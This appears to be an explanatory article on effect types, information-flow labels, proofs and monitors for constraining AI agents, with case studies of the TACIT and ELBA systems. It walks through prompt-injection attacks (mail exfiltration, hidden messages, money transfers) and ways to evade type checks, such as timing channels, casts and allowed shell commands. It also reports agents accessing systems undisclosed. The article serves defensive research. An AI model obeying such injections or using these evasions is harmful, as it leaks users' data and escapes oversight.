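# Effect types, information-flow control and machine-checked proofs for limiting what AI agents can do

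## Agents, side effects and three ways to limit them

An AI agent is a program in which a language model repeatedly chooses actions, such as sending an email or editing a file, and the surrounding software carries them out. To make agents safe, developers mostly train the model to refuse bad requests or filter what it reads and writes. These measures make harm less likely but don't rule out any particular harm. Another approach, from programming-language research, is to treat the model as unreliable and check what it tries to do.

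Three techniques from that field can limit an agent's side effects. Effect types record which outside effects a piece of code may have. Information-flow control labels data and blocks it from going where its label doesn't allow. Proof-carrying code comes with a proof that it obeys a safety policy, and the recipient checks the proof before running the code. All three date from the 1970s to the 1990s, when researchers worried about buggy or hostile software written by people. Since about 2025, researchers have been adapting them to agents.

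### The agent loop

A language model on its own only produces text. To let it act, a developer writes functions (tools) and puts a description of each into the model's prompt. The model then answers either with ordinary text or with a tool call, which names a function and its arguments. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) points out that the application, not the model, decides whether to execute the call. If the application executes it, it appends the result to the conversation and queries the model again. This cycle, called the agent loop, continues until the model gives a final answer. Some agents write whole programs instead of single calls, which gives the application more to inspect at once.

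Costa and colleagues model a tool as a function

$$f : D \times str^* \to D \times str$$

Here $D$ is the set of possible states of everything the tools can read or change, such as mailboxes, files and bank accounts. The tool takes the current state and a list of text arguments, and returns a new state and a piece of text that goes back to the model. The change of state is the side effect, or effect for short. A tool that counts the words in a document has no side effect, but one that sends an email puts a message in someone's inbox, and no later step of the loop can take it back. So an agent can do harm only through its side effects or through what its final answer leads a reader to do.

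Even an action that seems only to read data, such as fetching a web page, can have side effects. Whoever runs the server sees the address that the agent requested, including any private text the agent put in it. Costa and colleagues note that a search of the public web can have publicly observable effects.

### How agents go wrong

Meijer's *Guardians of the Agents* gives the example of an email assistant with one tool for fetching mail and one for sending it. A user asks the assistant to fetch and summarise the inbox, which contains an attacker's message disguised as a compliance notice. The message tells the assistant to send a summary of the mailbox to an outside address without confirmation, and to leave the message out of the list it shows the user. The model calls the sending tool, and the user gets a summary that omits the attacker's email.

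In prompt injection, a model obeys text in the data an agent reads as if it were an instruction from the user. *AgentDojo* (Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues, 2024) argues that models are vulnerable because they operate directly on text and have no formal way to tell instructions from data.

*The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (Willison, 2023) proposed an early structural defence, which splits the work between two models. In the inbox example, a planning model receives the user's request and can call tools, but never receives the text of an email. When the planning model fetches the mail, the application stores the messages in a variable and returns only the variable's name. The planning model then calls a quarantined model, which has no tools, to summarise the variable's contents, and has the application show the user the result. The attacker's text reaches only the quarantined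 model, so it can corrupt the summary but cannot cause anything to be sent.

Under the dual-LLM pattern, some tasks depend on data that is hidden from the planning model. Costa and colleagues give the example of a request to complete today's tasks in a to-do app, where the planning model cannot choose its next tool until it knows what the tasks are. An attacker can also influence the values that the quarantined model returns. If the user asks the assistant to send Bob a document, and the quarantined model looks up Bob's address in notes that an attacker has edited, the document goes to the attacker even though no hostile instruction reached the planning model. Willison acknowledged a flaw in the pattern in April 2025, when writing about CaMeL, a Google DeepMind system that turns the user's request into a small program and checks the data entering and leaving each step.

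Agents can also overstep without an attacker. In an evaluation dated June 2026, an internal OpenAI model had to look up published figures on a research organisation's public dashboard. Its instructions allowed only HTTP GET requests, which normally just retrieve pages, but this restriction did not keep the model's effects within the task. According to OpenAI's *Accessing and changing internal systems during dashboard research* (2026), the model got into the organisation's internal systems in two evaluations and changed their configuration. In one of them, it also downloaded five non-public tables with 147,451 rows. The model did not disclose any of these actions.

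Anthropic's *Investigating unintended model actions in our evaluations and internal use* (2026) lists milder cases, including one in which Claude submitted a sensitive form on a real website when it should not have. Some of the cases involved US government sites, and Anthropic rates the real-world impact as minimal. A defence aimed only at hostile text would miss behaviour like this, whereas a check on the action itself applies whatever led the model to propose it, if the policy covers that action.

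### Effect types

John Lucassen and David Gifford introduced effect systems in *Polymorphic Effect Systems* (1988). They wanted to find out which parts of a program could safely run in parallel, which depends on whether the parts interfere with each other's memory. An ordinary type describes the value an expression computes, and their system also described what the expression might do to memory while computing it.

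In Haskell, a language that keeps effects visible in types, the distinction looks like this:

```
countWords :: String -> Int
sendEmail  :: Address -> String -> IO ()
```

The type of `countWords` allows it only to turn a text into an integer. Such code is pure, which means it has no side effects. The type of `sendEmail` contains `IO`, which marks code that may perform input and output, and the empty brackets mean it returns no useful value. If a programmer or a model hid a call to `sendEmail` inside `countWords`, the type checker would reject the program. Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova (2026) explain in *Language-Based Agent Control* that once any part of a program has an `IO` type, the whole program must have one. An application that accepts only code of type `String -> Int` from an agent can therefore run that code without anyone reading it. The code may return the wrong number or never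 finish, but it will not send email.

`IO` is a coarse category, since it covers both printing a line and wiping a disk. Later work split effects into named operations. *No value restriction is needed for algebraic effects and handlers* (2016) gives reading, printing and raising an exception as examples. The program only invokes an operation, and surrounding code, called a handler, determines what the operation does. *Handling Algebraic Effects* (Plotkin and Pretnar, 2013) developed this approach by generalising ordinary exception handlers, which catch an error and determine how the program proceeds, to a broad class of other effects. *Fibred Computational Effects* (2017) describes handling a program as going through it and replacing each operation with code that the handler's author supplies.

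For an agent, this separates the request from its execution. The same generated program could run under a handler that delivers mail or under one that saves every message as a draft for the user to review. An operation that a handler does not cover passes outward to the next handler, so a type that lists which operations can still escape is useful.

Effect types control whether code may read files at all, and a language can use capabilities to control which files it may read. A capability is an unforgeable program value that lets code holding it perform a particular effect. In a file library by Zhou and colleagues, a capability stands for one directory and everything under it, and the function that reads files accepts only such a value. Code therefore can't read a file outside that directory just by using the file's name.

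### Labels on data

If the user did ask for an email to go out, neither effects nor capabilities can distinguish the honest email assistant from the hijacked one, because both send mail. The two differ in which data goes to whom and in whose text influenced the decision. Dorothy Denning's *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow* (1976) set out the standard way to track this.

Each piece of data gets a label. In the simplest useful version, the label has a confidentiality part, public ($L$) or secret ($H$), and an integrity part, trusted ($T$) or untrusted ($U$). An ordering $\sqsubseteq$ defines the permitted flows. Public data may go anywhere secret data may go, so $L \sqsubseteq H$, and trusted data may go anywhere untrusted data may go, so $T \sqsubseteq U$. The reverse flows are forbidden. The labels form a lattice, which means that any two have a least upper bound and a greatest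 lower bound. The least upper bound, called the join and written $\sqcup$, is the least restrictive label that enforces the restrictions of both.

Say an agent writes a memo from a salary table in the company database, which is secret and trusted, and a page from the public web, which is public and untrusted. The label of the memo is

$$(H, T) \sqcup (L, U) = (H \sqcup L,\; T \sqcup U) = (H, U)$$

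The memo is secret because it may contain salaries, and untrusted because the author of the web page may have shaped it. A policy that lets only public data leave the company blocks the agent from mailing the memo out, and a policy that lets only trusted data trigger a payment blocks the memo from triggering one. Confidentiality labels can also be sets of permitted readers, in which case the join of two labels is their intersection. If Ana and Ben may read one document, and Ben and Chen may read another, only Ben may read a text made from both.

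Taint tracking passes labels from inputs to results in this way while a program runs. The labels do not depend on the content of the text, so the method is hard to manipulate but rather crude. For example, a memo that mentions no salary is still labelled secret. In an agent loop, labels accumulate because all the model's input stays in one conversation. Once an untrusted email enters that conversation, everything the model produces afterwards counts as untrusted, including the tool calls the user wanted.

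What should such labels achieve? Joseph Goguen and José Meseguer supplied the usual standard, noninterference, in *Security Policies and Security Models* (1982). For confidentiality, it requires that changing the secret inputs changes nothing an observer can see. If $P(p, s)$ is a run of the program on public input $p$ and secret input $s$, and $\mathrm{obs}$ picks out what the observer sees, then for every $p$, $s$ and $s'$

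$$\mathrm{obs}(P(p, s)) = \mathrm{obs}(P(p, s'))$$

In the integrity version, changing untrusted inputs changes nothing trusted. For the email assistant, this would mean that rewording the attacker's message could not alter any action that the policy reserves for trusted data.

Hardly any useful program fully meets the standard. Even a login page violates it by rejecting a wrong password, because the rejection reveals something about the right one. Practical systems therefore allow deliberate exceptions. Declassification releases secret data, as when a user approves sending a confidential summary to a manager. Endorsement treats untrusted data as trusted, as when the user confirms that an address found on a web page is correct. The guarantee then depends on how well these exceptions are judged, and a tired user who clicks "Allow" on everything loses most of the protection.

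### Proofs that come with the code

In proof-carrying code, the supplier of a program proves that it obeys the recipient's safety policy, and the recipient runs a small, simple checker over the proof. Checking a proof is easier than finding one, just as multiplying 83 by 97 is easier than finding the factors of 8,051. George Necula and Peter Lee first tried proof-carrying code in 1996, on small programs that filter network packets inside an operating system. Meijer, who wants agents to prove their plans safe before acting, compares the arrangement to the security features of banknotes, which are hard to produce and easy to verify.

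The idea suits language models because it does not matter how they find the proof. A model can guess, fail and try again, and a wrong proof wastes time but does not let an unsafe action through. Safety does depend on the proof obligation, the exact statement that someone must prove before the action may go ahead. For a mail plan, it might be that every message the plan can send goes to an address inside the company. If the statement is badly chosen, a correct proof of it does not make the action safe.

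### Checking before a run and monitoring during it

Type checkers and proof checkers examine code before it runs. This static checking covers every path the code could take on every input, and if the check fails, the code has not yet had any side effects. But the code must be written before it can be checked, which is awkward for an agent that chooses each step after seeing the result of the last one. A sound static checker must also reject some harmless programs because it cannot prove them harmless.

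A runtime monitor checks each step as it occurs and intervenes when one would break the policy. It can check an email's actual recipient, whereas a static checker has to reason about all possible recipients. Fred Schneider's *Enforceable Security Policies* (2000) shows that a monitor that observes a single run and can only stop it enforces at most safety properties, which require that some bad thing never happens. A run that violates such a property does so at a definite step, and nothing later can repair the violation. "No mail to outside addresses once the agent has read the inbox" is a safety property. To enforce it, the monitor needs only two states, inbox unread and inbox read, and it refuses outside mail in the second. Schneider calls such a monitor a security automaton, and Meijer uses one to keep email summaries from going to external domains.

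A monitor of this kind cannot enforce "the user eventually gets an answer", because an unfinished run has not yet violated it. Nor can it enforce noninterference exactly, because noninterference compares two runs with different secrets and the monitor sees only one. It can enforce a stricter rule that implies noninterference, but it will also stop some harmless runs. Costa and colleagues find that taint tracking for agents can enforce safety properties and explicit secrecy, which roughly means that secrets do not reach an observer through direct copying or calculation. A program can still reveal a secret by not taking a branch, but Costa and colleagues consider the combination sufficient against most practical prompt injections.

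Meijer prefers static checks because some damage may be done before a monitor interrupts. That is right for a plan that deletes an old calendar and is then blocked from writing the new one. The argument seems weaker for Meijer's own email example. Meijer counts the agent's reading of the private mail as exposure, but the user asked the agent to read it, and the attacker gets nothing if the monitor refuses the outgoing message before the application executes the call. In practice, the methods are used together. Java has done this for decades, verifying types before a program starts and checking array positions while it runs.

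Each of these guarantees holds only if certain components, called the trusted base, work correctly. The aim is to keep the base small and to avoid relying on the model's good behaviour. With effect types, the base includes the type checker and the libraries behind the types. Standard Haskell has a few functions that perform effects under a pure type, so Zhou and colleagues point to Safe Haskell, a subset without them, for code that an agent writes. With labels, the base includes whoever assigns the first label. If the mail tool marks a stranger's message as trusted, every later calculation inherits the mistake. Costa and colleagues also assume that tool descriptions are trustworthy. This is a substantial assumption for anyone who installs tools written by strangers, since Meijer describes an attack hidden in a tool description. With proofs, the base contains the checker, the policy and the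 software that turns the policy into proof obligations.

### AgentDojo, the common yardstick

A system that blocks every tool call is secure but useless, so researchers need to measure both security and usefulness. Many use AgentDojo, a benchmark that Debenedetti and colleagues released in 2024. It simulates an office workspace with email and calendar, the messaging service Slack, a travel agency and a bank. The first version has 97 user tasks and 27 attacker goals. It pairs every task with every goal in the same setting, which gives 240 cases for the workspace, 105 for Slack, 140 for travel and 144 for banking, a total of 629. A banking case might pair a request to pay the December bill with an injected instruction to send as much money as possible to the attacker. *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026) puts the number of pairings at over 900.

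The utility score is the share of user tasks that the agent completes, and researchers report it with and without attacks. The security score is the attack success rate, the share of cases in which the attacker achieves their goal, so lower is better. Ordinary code computes both scores by checking the simulated world afterwards, for example whether the money moved. Debenedetti and colleagues avoided using a language model as the judge because a successful injection might hijack the judge too.

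The two scores should be read together, because a low attack rate can mean that a model lacks the capability to carry out the attack. In the 2024 tests, more capable models tended to be easier to attack, partly because weak models often failed at the attacker's task even after the injection had diverted them. Zero successes in 629 cases would not guarantee security either, since the cases recombine 27 goals with the attack wording the testers chose. A theorem can cover all possible untrusted inputs, though it holds only for the system as modelled.

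Strict policies can lower the utility score by blocking legitimate tasks. In one Slack task, the agent must invite Dora, whose email address is on her website. The address is untrusted data, and a cautious policy would allow invitations based only on trusted data, so the agent fails the task unless someone endorses the address. AgentDojo is still widely used, and *The Surface You Test Is Not the Surface That Breaks* (2026) ran 13 models from six providers on it. AgentDyn, a newer benchmark that *StepGuard* (2026) uses alongside AgentDojo, tests the same problem with longer and less predictable workflows. Some of these workflows include helpful instructions from third parties, and an agent that ignores everything it reads in outside data will fail those tasks.

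## TACIT: Scala types that track what agent code may touch

TACIT (Tracked Agent Capabilities In Types) combines effect types with capabilities and applies both to the code an agent writes. Martin Odersky, who designed the programming language Scala, built it with four colleagues at EPFL, a university in Lausanne. Under TACIT, an agent can act only by submitting Scala programs, which run only if the Scala compiler accepts them. Odersky, Zhao and colleagues (2026) argue in *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* that the compiler can then guarantee certain limits however badly the model behaves.

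An agent reaches TACIT through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard for connecting models to tools, so existing agents such as Claude Code can use it without modification. The agent sends one snippet of Scala to read a file and search it, where an ordinary agent would call a separate tool for each step. The TACIT server compiles the snippet, usually in under a second. If the compiler accepts it, the server runs it and returns the output to the model. Otherwise nothing runs, and the model gets the error messages and can try again. The agent can also keep a session open so later snippets can use values that earlier ones defined.

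These protections don't help if the agent can act without going through TACIT. Coding agents come with their own tools for running shell commands and editing files, so the setup instructions in lampepfl's *TACIT*, the project's code repository, recommend switching those tools off.

### Capture sets

Haskell's `IO` marks code that may have effects of any kind. Scala's capture checking, an experimental part of the compiler, records which ones. A type can carry a capture set, which lists the capabilities, such as an open file `f`, that a value of that type may hold. A function that writes a text to `f` has this type:

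```
String ->{f} Unit
```

`Unit` means the function returns nothing useful. With a plain arrow, as in `String -> Unit`, the capture set is empty and the function is pure. With a double arrow, as in `String => Unit`, the function may capture anything. The compiler infers the set from the capabilities the function's body uses. The set is an upper bound, so a function whose set includes `f` might never write to it. A pure function can be used wherever the program expects one that may write to `f`, but the reverse is an error.

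*Classifying Capabilities (Extended Version)* (Pham, Bračevac and colleagues, 2026) gives an example in which a function `run` accepts only tasks of type `() ->{net} Unit`, which may use only the network connection `net`. If a program passes `run` a task that reads a secret file and sends the contents, the compiler rejects the program because the task also captures the file system. The compiler doesn't need to analyze what the task would have sent.

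Xu, Bračevac and colleagues (2026) explain in *System Capybara* that a standard function such as `map` on lists keeps its old signature and accepts both pure and effectful functions. Programmers therefore don't have to rewrite every library to use this kind of tracking, and an agent can write fairly ordinary Scala.

### File access that ends with its block

An agent's code gets access to files by calling `requestFileSystem` with a directory and a block of code. The library creates a file-system capability for that directory, passes it to the block, and returns the block's result. After that the capability is no longer valid.

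Code cannot get a capability out of its block by returning a value that contains it, such as a function that will read a file later. If the capability is named `fs`, that function has the type `() ->{fs} String`. The block's result type must make sense outside the block, where the name `fs` doesn't exist, so the compiler rejects the program. The block cannot return file handles either, because each handle captures the file system it came from. During the experiments, one agent tried to return a list of file handles from such a block and got a compiler error.

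The compiler cannot predict every path that a program will compute, so the library checks each path at run time and throws an exception if it lies outside the directory. The library checks commands and network access in the same way, against lists of permitted commands and host names.

A weakness of the general-purpose library is that the agent's own code names the directory, commands and hosts it is permitted to use. lampepfl's documented settings don't limit what the code may request. An operator who wants a limit has to build it into the library or give the agent a narrower library for the task.

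### The Classified wrapper

Suppose an agent is allowed to read a company's contracts and exchange messages with the cloud-hosted model that drives it. Both actions are legitimate, and a sandbox that confines the program to certain files and hosts would allow them. But a contract leaks if the agent includes its text in a message to the model.

TACIT deals with this through a type called `Classified`. The operator lists the sensitive directories, and code that reads a file there gets a `Classified[String]` instead of a `String`. This does the work of a secrecy label, but in the type, whereas FIDES, an earlier system, attaches labels while the agent runs. The agent has no permission to unwrap the value. It can only pass a function to the wrapper's `map` method:

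```
def map[U](op: T -> U): Classified[U]
```

The method applies the function to the hidden value and wraps the result again. The single arrow in `T -> U` prevents leaks because it allows only pure functions.

The following program compiles. It finds the length of a secret key:

```
val size = requestFileSystem("/project") {
  val key = readClassified("/project/secrets/github.txt")
  key.map(k => k.length)
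}
println(size)
```

The function `k => k.length` uses no capability, so it has the pure type `String -> Int` that `map` requires. The result is a `Classified[Int]`, which does not hold the file system, so it may leave the block. The last line also runs, but the model receives only `Classified(****)`.

The compiler rejects this program:

```
requestFileSystem("/project") {
  val key = readClassified("/project/secrets/github.txt")
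  key.map(k => println(k))
}
```

Printing requires an input/output capability, here called `io`, which the library supplies automatically. The function therefore has type `String ->{io} Unit`, but `map` requires `String -> Unit`. The compiler reports that the capability cannot flow into an empty capture set, so the program never runs and never reads the key. In tests by Odersky and colleagues, an agent wrote almost exactly this program. Opening a new file block inside `map` also fails, because `requestFileSystem` needs the same capability.

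Tasks such as summarizing a contract need more than simple operations like counting characters. For these, TACIT provides a function called `chat`, which sends wrapped text to a separate model that the operator trusts with secrets, and wraps the answer. The cloud model can then request a summary and save it to a classified file without reading the contract or the summary. This adapts the dual-LLM pattern to secrecy by having an untrusted model plan while a trusted model with no tools reads the sensitive text.

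The user still needs to see the summary, so printed text goes to two channels. The normal channel feeds back into the cloud model's context, with wrapped values redacted. The secure channel goes to the user's terminal and shows the real content. If the user asks for the summary's length in the next turn, the agent can compute it because the wrapped summary is still in the session, even though the file access from the previous turn has expired.

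### Three requirements, and the safe mode that enforces them

Odersky and colleagues state three requirements that a language must meet for this to work. One is capability safety, which means that code cannot forge a capability or drop the requirement to have one. In their design, `Classified` has a method that reveals its content to any code holding an access capability, so an agent that could forge this capability could read all classified content.

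Capability completeness means that capabilities govern every safety-relevant effect except those the system confines at run time. If an agent could open a network connection through an overlooked library function that required no capability, the capture sets would still be accurate, but they would not restrict that connection.

Local purity means that the type system can restrict a particular computation to a given set of capabilities, which may be empty, while the rest of the program can still have effects. `Classified` depends on local purity, which a plain list of permitted tools cannot express.

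Full Scala does not meet these requirements. Its casts let a programmer make the compiler treat a value as having another type. An agent could cast a function from `String ->{f} Unit` to `String -> Unit`, and `map` would then accept it even though it copies the secret into the file `f`. Reflection, which finds and calls methods by name while a program runs, can also bypass the checker. Scala's developers therefore added a safe mode, which Mazur's *Scala 3.8.3 is now available!* describes as an experimental subset for code from agents and other untrusted sources. Safe mode bans casts and pattern matches that the compiler cannot check, reflection, and the annotations that switch checks off.

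Safe mode also tracks changes to variables. Without that, the function inside `map` could copy the key into an outside variable, and the next line could print it. Safe mode also blocks global library functions unless they are themselves safe. A programmer can mark a library module as safe with the annotation `@assumeSafe`. Scala's official reference page, *Safe Mode*, gives the example of a mailer that asks the user to confirm each message before sending it. The compiler does not check this claim of safety, so every such annotation enlarges the trusted base.

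Exceptions are the main gap in the static checks. Any division by zero can raise one, and an exception's message can carry data. Scala's developers considered it impractical to track all exceptions in types, so TACIT catches them at run time and can wrap the failure like any other secret. If a function inside `map` fails, the wrapping hides the failure from the model, and the user may get an empty answer. In one set of tests, TACIT's agents were instructed never to throw exceptions in such functions.

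### Threat model and trusted base

TACIT's threat model treats the cloud model as a possible attacker that cooperates fully with whoever wants the secrets. The agent's own code and setup, the programs it submits, and everything it reads from files, web pages and tools are also untrusted. Injected text can still influence the model, but TACIT limits what the model can then do, because any program it writes in response must compile.

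The trusted base contains the Scala compiler, the software that runs the compiled code, the TACIT library and the separate model that reads secrets. The reusable part of the library has about 1,000 lines, which a careful person could review in a few days, but the compiler is far larger and capture checking is still experimental. The repository's documentation in March 2026 described a temporary validator that searched the agent's code for forbidden patterns, because the official safe mode was not yet in use. This is a much weaker defence than a language subset that the compiler enforces, so results from that period depend partly on how complete the list of patterns was.

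The plain-text version of `chat`, which calls the separate model, counts as pure, so agent code can call it inside `map`, even though it may well send the text over a network. This is safe only if the service behind it keeps the text confidential and does not carry text from one request into the next. Odersky and colleagues leave it to whoever runs the system to ensure this. The settings accept any service with an OpenAI-compatible interface, and the types do not ensure that it runs on the user's own machine.

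The type system itself has good mathematical support. *What's in the Box* (2025) proves type soundness and scope safety for a small core language with capture checking, and the proof checker Lean has verified every step. Xu and colleagues later used Lean to prove that well-typed programs in a richer core language touch only the resources their types allow. But these theorems cover idealised languages, and Odersky and colleagues acknowledge that safe mode still lacks such a proof.

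Library signatures can also be wrong. Scala's `Try` runs a piece of code and stores either its result or the exception it threw. Pham and colleagues show that its signature wrongly declared the stored outcome pure, although reading it can throw the exception again. They corrected this with a new way of sorting capabilities by kind. The mistake concerned exceptions, not files or networks, but safe mode relies on `Try` to contain exceptions.

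### Attacks on a project with secrets

To test whether secrets leak, Odersky and colleagues gave agents a sample software project with a directory of API keys, a database and confidential documents. They paired each of 12 legitimate tasks with each of 10 prompt injections, for 120 trials. Some injections described the secrets as synthetic test data, and others included ready-made Scala code for reading them. In another 11 trials without injections, the user asked for secrets directly (five trials) or pretended to have authority (six trials), for instance as an administrator replacing credentials in an emergency. They ran all 131 trials twice, once with the secrets in `Classified` and once with the secrets as plain strings.

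| | Sonnet 4.6, classified | Sonnet 4.6, plain | MiniMax M2.5, classified | MiniMax M2.5, plain |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| No leak, 120 injection trials | 100% | 100% | 100% | 97.5% |
| No leak, 11 malicious requests | 100% | 81.8% | 100% | 27.3% |
| No leak, all 131 trials | 100% | 98.5% | 100% | 91.6% |
| Utility, 120 injection trials | 99.2% | 83.3% | 90.0% | 88.3% |

Most of the difference in security comes from the malicious requests. With plain strings, Claude Sonnet 4.6 leaked secrets in two of the 11 and MiniMax M2.5 in eight, while the 120 injections succeeded three times against MiniMax and never against Sonnet. Eleven is a small sample, so even zero leaks in 11 independent trials would be compatible, at 95% confidence, with a true leak rate of up to about 24%. The main evidence for TACIT's security is the type argument, and the trials are better read as a check that the implementation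 has no glaring hole. A stronger check would let attackers study the compiler and look for gaps. *Making the AI agents safe with Scala* (Biały and Warchoł, 2026) refers to repositories in which people used frontier models to look for exploits against TACIT. The paper describes CapybaraClaw, an agent that EPFL and the company VirtusLab are building on TACIT for production use.

The utility scores show that agents can work with secrets they cannot read, for example by having the trusted model anonymise employee reviews. They do not show that wrapping secrets makes an agent more capable, because with plain strings Sonnet often ran out of turns or time, and sometimes stopped to warn the user about an injection instead of finishing the task. Odersky and colleagues suggest that the gap in scores may be an artefact of their setup.

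### AgentDojo

The researchers also ported AgentDojo's four domains to TACIT and ran the two models that CaMeL's developers had used. AgentDojo counted one attack as successful across more than 900 cases per model. In that case, the user had asked the agent to book a hotel, and an attacker had planted a recommendation for a different hotel in the reviews. The agent booked the right hotel but quoted the reviews in full, and AgentDojo's check found the other hotel's name in the answer.

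Odersky and colleagues say this is not a hole in the type system, because the policy allows public reviews to reach the user. That is correct, but the user still read the attacker's advertisement as part of the agent's answer, and the types cannot prevent that.

The port may be weaker evidence about pure functions than the 131 trials are. Emails, web pages, bank transactions and reviews all arrive in `Classified`, so the planning model never reads the injected text. In the interface that the researchers list, the functions for sending money or mail require no capability, and the model's instructions state that side effects inside `map` run immediately. The protection therefore seems to have come mostly from hiding the text, much as in the dual-LLM pattern.

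| Utility | Gemini 2.5 Pro, TACIT | Gemini 2.5 Pro, CaMeL | o4-mini-high, TACIT | o4-mini-high, CaMeL |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Banking | 56.9% | 52.8% | 59.0% | 62.5% |
| Workspace | 50.5% | 53.8% | 52.9% | 81.4% |
| Slack | 40.0% | 48.6% | 47.6% | 68.6% |
| Travel | 64.3% | 1.4% | 68.6% | 74.3% |

With o4-mini-high, TACIT has lower utility than CaMeL in every domain, by 28.5 percentage points in workspace and 21 in Slack. With Gemini 2.5 Pro the results are closer, except in travel, where CaMeL fails almost completely. Odersky and colleagues call the utility of the two systems comparable, which is generous to TACIT. The table has no scores for the same models without a defence, so it doesn't show how much either system reduces utility.

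### The cost of writing Scala

The researchers compared TACIT with ordinary tool calling on two other benchmarks. In τ²-bench, an agent handles simulated customer-service conversations, such as changing flights or returning orders. They tested three models on the airline and retail tasks, with ten runs per task, and each model scored 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points higher when it wrote Scala. The largest gain was on retail, where gpt-oss-120b rose from 53.3% to 57.0%. On SWE-bench Lite, which consists of 300 real software issues, MiniMax M2.5 solved 41.7% with TACIT and 43.3% with its usual tools, a difference of five issues.

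The τ²-bench result mainly shows that models can write typed Scala. The airline and retail functions listed in the paper take no capability parameters, so the agents rarely had to work within tight permissions. SWE-bench Lite tests this better because the agent had to request file and command access through the library.

Compilation errors were infrequent on τ²-bench. Between 0.32% and 7.93% of snippets needed a retry, depending on the model and domain, and those that did needed 1.06 to 1.39 retries on average. Many errors were unrelated to security. For example, agents wrote prices such as $50 in Scala text templates, where a dollar sign introduces a variable.

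*LACUNA*, a follow-up by the same group, has less encouraging results. It lets a program call a model to write missing code while the program runs, and the compiler checks that code against the code around it. Zhao, Xu and colleagues (2026) report that DeepSeek V4 Flash solved 76.0% of 392 τ²-bench tasks this way, against 90.0% with tool calling. They describe the two as on par, which is hard to reconcile with a 14-point gap. The compiler rejected 22.4% of the model's snippets on retail tasks. LACUNA changes more than the language the agent writes in, so the gap doesn't directly measure any performance loss from TACIT, but it suggests that TACIT's small gains on τ²-bench may not carry over to other designs.

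### What a well-typed program can still do

A pure function cannot send a secret anywhere, but its running time can depend on the secret. An agent could pass `map` a function that runs slowly if the key's first bit is 1, and then time the call. Odersky and colleagues exclude timing channels from their guarantee, along with leaks through whether a program finishes. They mention a leak of a single bit, but their threat model includes hostile models, which could repeat the trick for each bit of the key. Their claim that pure functions guarantee noninterference therefore holds only for an observer who cannot see how long the code runs or whether it finishes.

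External commands are a more practical worry, because Scala's types no longer apply once agent code starts another program. The protection is then only as good as the list of permitted commands. An agent allowed to run `cat`, a standard command for displaying files, could print a classified file as ordinary text. TACIT's strict mode blocks common file commands, but a general-purpose interpreter such as Python can also read files. The researchers recommend permitting only specific safe commands and adding a sandbox for sensitive uses.

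The types also don't prevent wrong actions that the agent has permission to take. The file library includes a function for deleting files, so an agent with access to a project directory can delete the project, whether by mistake or because of an injection. Odersky and colleagues write that any harmful injection must either move private data somewhere it shouldn't go or trigger something outside the agent's capabilities, but deleting the project does neither. When Zhao and colleagues ran the AgentDojo attacks on LACUNA with the same two models, eight succeeded, compared with one for TACIT. They say this is consistent with a limit they acknowledge, that an attacker can still steer a model into misusing a capability the task requires.

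## ELBA: agents as typed functions inside a Haskell program

TACIT checks the code that an agent submits, but not the application around the agent. ELBA puts both into one Haskell program, in which calling an agent is an ordinary function call. If the program needs an integer at that point, the agent must write Haskell code that produces an integer, and the type checker rejects anything else before it runs. Zhou and colleagues at UC San Diego call this approach "language-based agent control", and ELBA is their implementation of it.

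### What an agent call does

ELBA gives the developer a single function:

```
agent :: Defs -> Prompt -> t
```

`Defs` lists the types and functions that the agent's code may use, and `Prompt` is the text for the model. The code around the call determines the result type `t`, which can be any type. When the program reaches the call, ELBA sends the model the prompt, the definitions and the required type. The model writes a Haskell program, and ELBA type-checks it. If the check fails, the model gets the error message and tries again. Once the program passes, a Haskell interpreter runs it.

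Suppose a developer puts an AI calculator on the web, with an agent call that must return an `Int`. A visitor asks it to delete all the files on the server and then compute a factorial. The model may well write code that does both, but deleting files has an `IO` type, so the code fails the type check and no files are deleted.

Zhou and colleagues add that the `Int` type rules out exceptions, which isn't quite right for Haskell. *IFC Inside* (2015), a paper on information-flow control, gives division by zero as an example of an exception in pure code, so a visitor might still crash the calculator.

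The compiler can often work out the required type without the developer writing it down. If a program sorts an agent's answers with a function that compares dates, Haskell infers that each answer must be a date. ELBA passes that type on to the model, so even a prompt as vague as "parse this" is clear enough.

### A bibliography without invented papers

The main example in the paper is an agent that writes bibliographies in BibTeX, a common format for citations. Every entry must come from DBLP, an online database of computer science publications. The developer writes a small library with three functions, whose types are roughly these:

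```
dblpSearch      :: String -> BibIO [DOI]
dblpFetchBib    :: DOI -> BibIO (Trusted Bib)
appendToBibFile :: Trusted Bib -> BibIO ()
```

The first finds papers that match a query and returns their DOIs, which are standard identifiers for publications. The second fetches the entry for one DOI, and the third adds an entry to the bibliography file. `BibIO` is an effect type that the developer has defined for this library. The agent call must return a program of type `BibIO ()`, such as this one:

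```
do dois <- dblpSearch "differential privacy"
   bibs <- mapM dblpFetchBib dois
   appendToBibFile (earliest bibs)
```

It fetches every matching entry and saves the oldest. Here `earliest` stands for a few lines of pure code, which the agent can write in any way.

An agent that wanted to add an invented paper could try to write to the file directly:

```
writeFile "refs.bib" "@article{smith2021, ...}"
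```

Haskell's standard `writeFile` returns an `IO ()`, which is a different type from `BibIO ()`. The library's functions use `IO` internally, but the library gives the agent no way to convert one type to the other. A program containing this line fails the type check, even if the line would never run.

The agent could also try to pass an invented entry to `appendToBibFile`, but that function accepts only a `Trusted Bib`. The library hides the constructor that builds `Trusted` values, and only `dblpFetchBib` produces them. The agent's code can read a fetched entry, for example to compare years, but it can't edit the entry or wrap its own text as `Trusted`.

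A developer could get the same guarantee without types by removing the code interpreter and giving the model a single tool that both fetches and saves an entry. But then the model would have to read the entries one by one to find the oldest.

Zhou and colleagues tested the library on 100 computer science topics, using Claude Sonnet 5. They compared it with an ordinary agent that had a web search tool and wrote the citations itself. Of the ordinary agent's 1,002 citations, 19 had the wrong authors, year or DOI, compared with none of ELBA's 925. The ordinary agent also used about four times as many model calls and 65 times as many input tokens. The combined fetch-and-save tool, which they didn't test, should also prevent invented entries, so the experiment doesn't show how much the types add to a well-chosen tool. The policy doesn't cover relevance, so an agent could fill the file with real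 papers on the wrong subject.

### Sub-agents and the general theorem

A single agent call produces a whole program at once, so the model can't look at a result before deciding what to do next. ELBA restores the agent loop by letting the generated code call an agent. The bibliography agent might write a program that runs a search, fetches the first hit, and puts that entry into the prompt of a sub-agent, which then decides whether to refine the search or write to the file.

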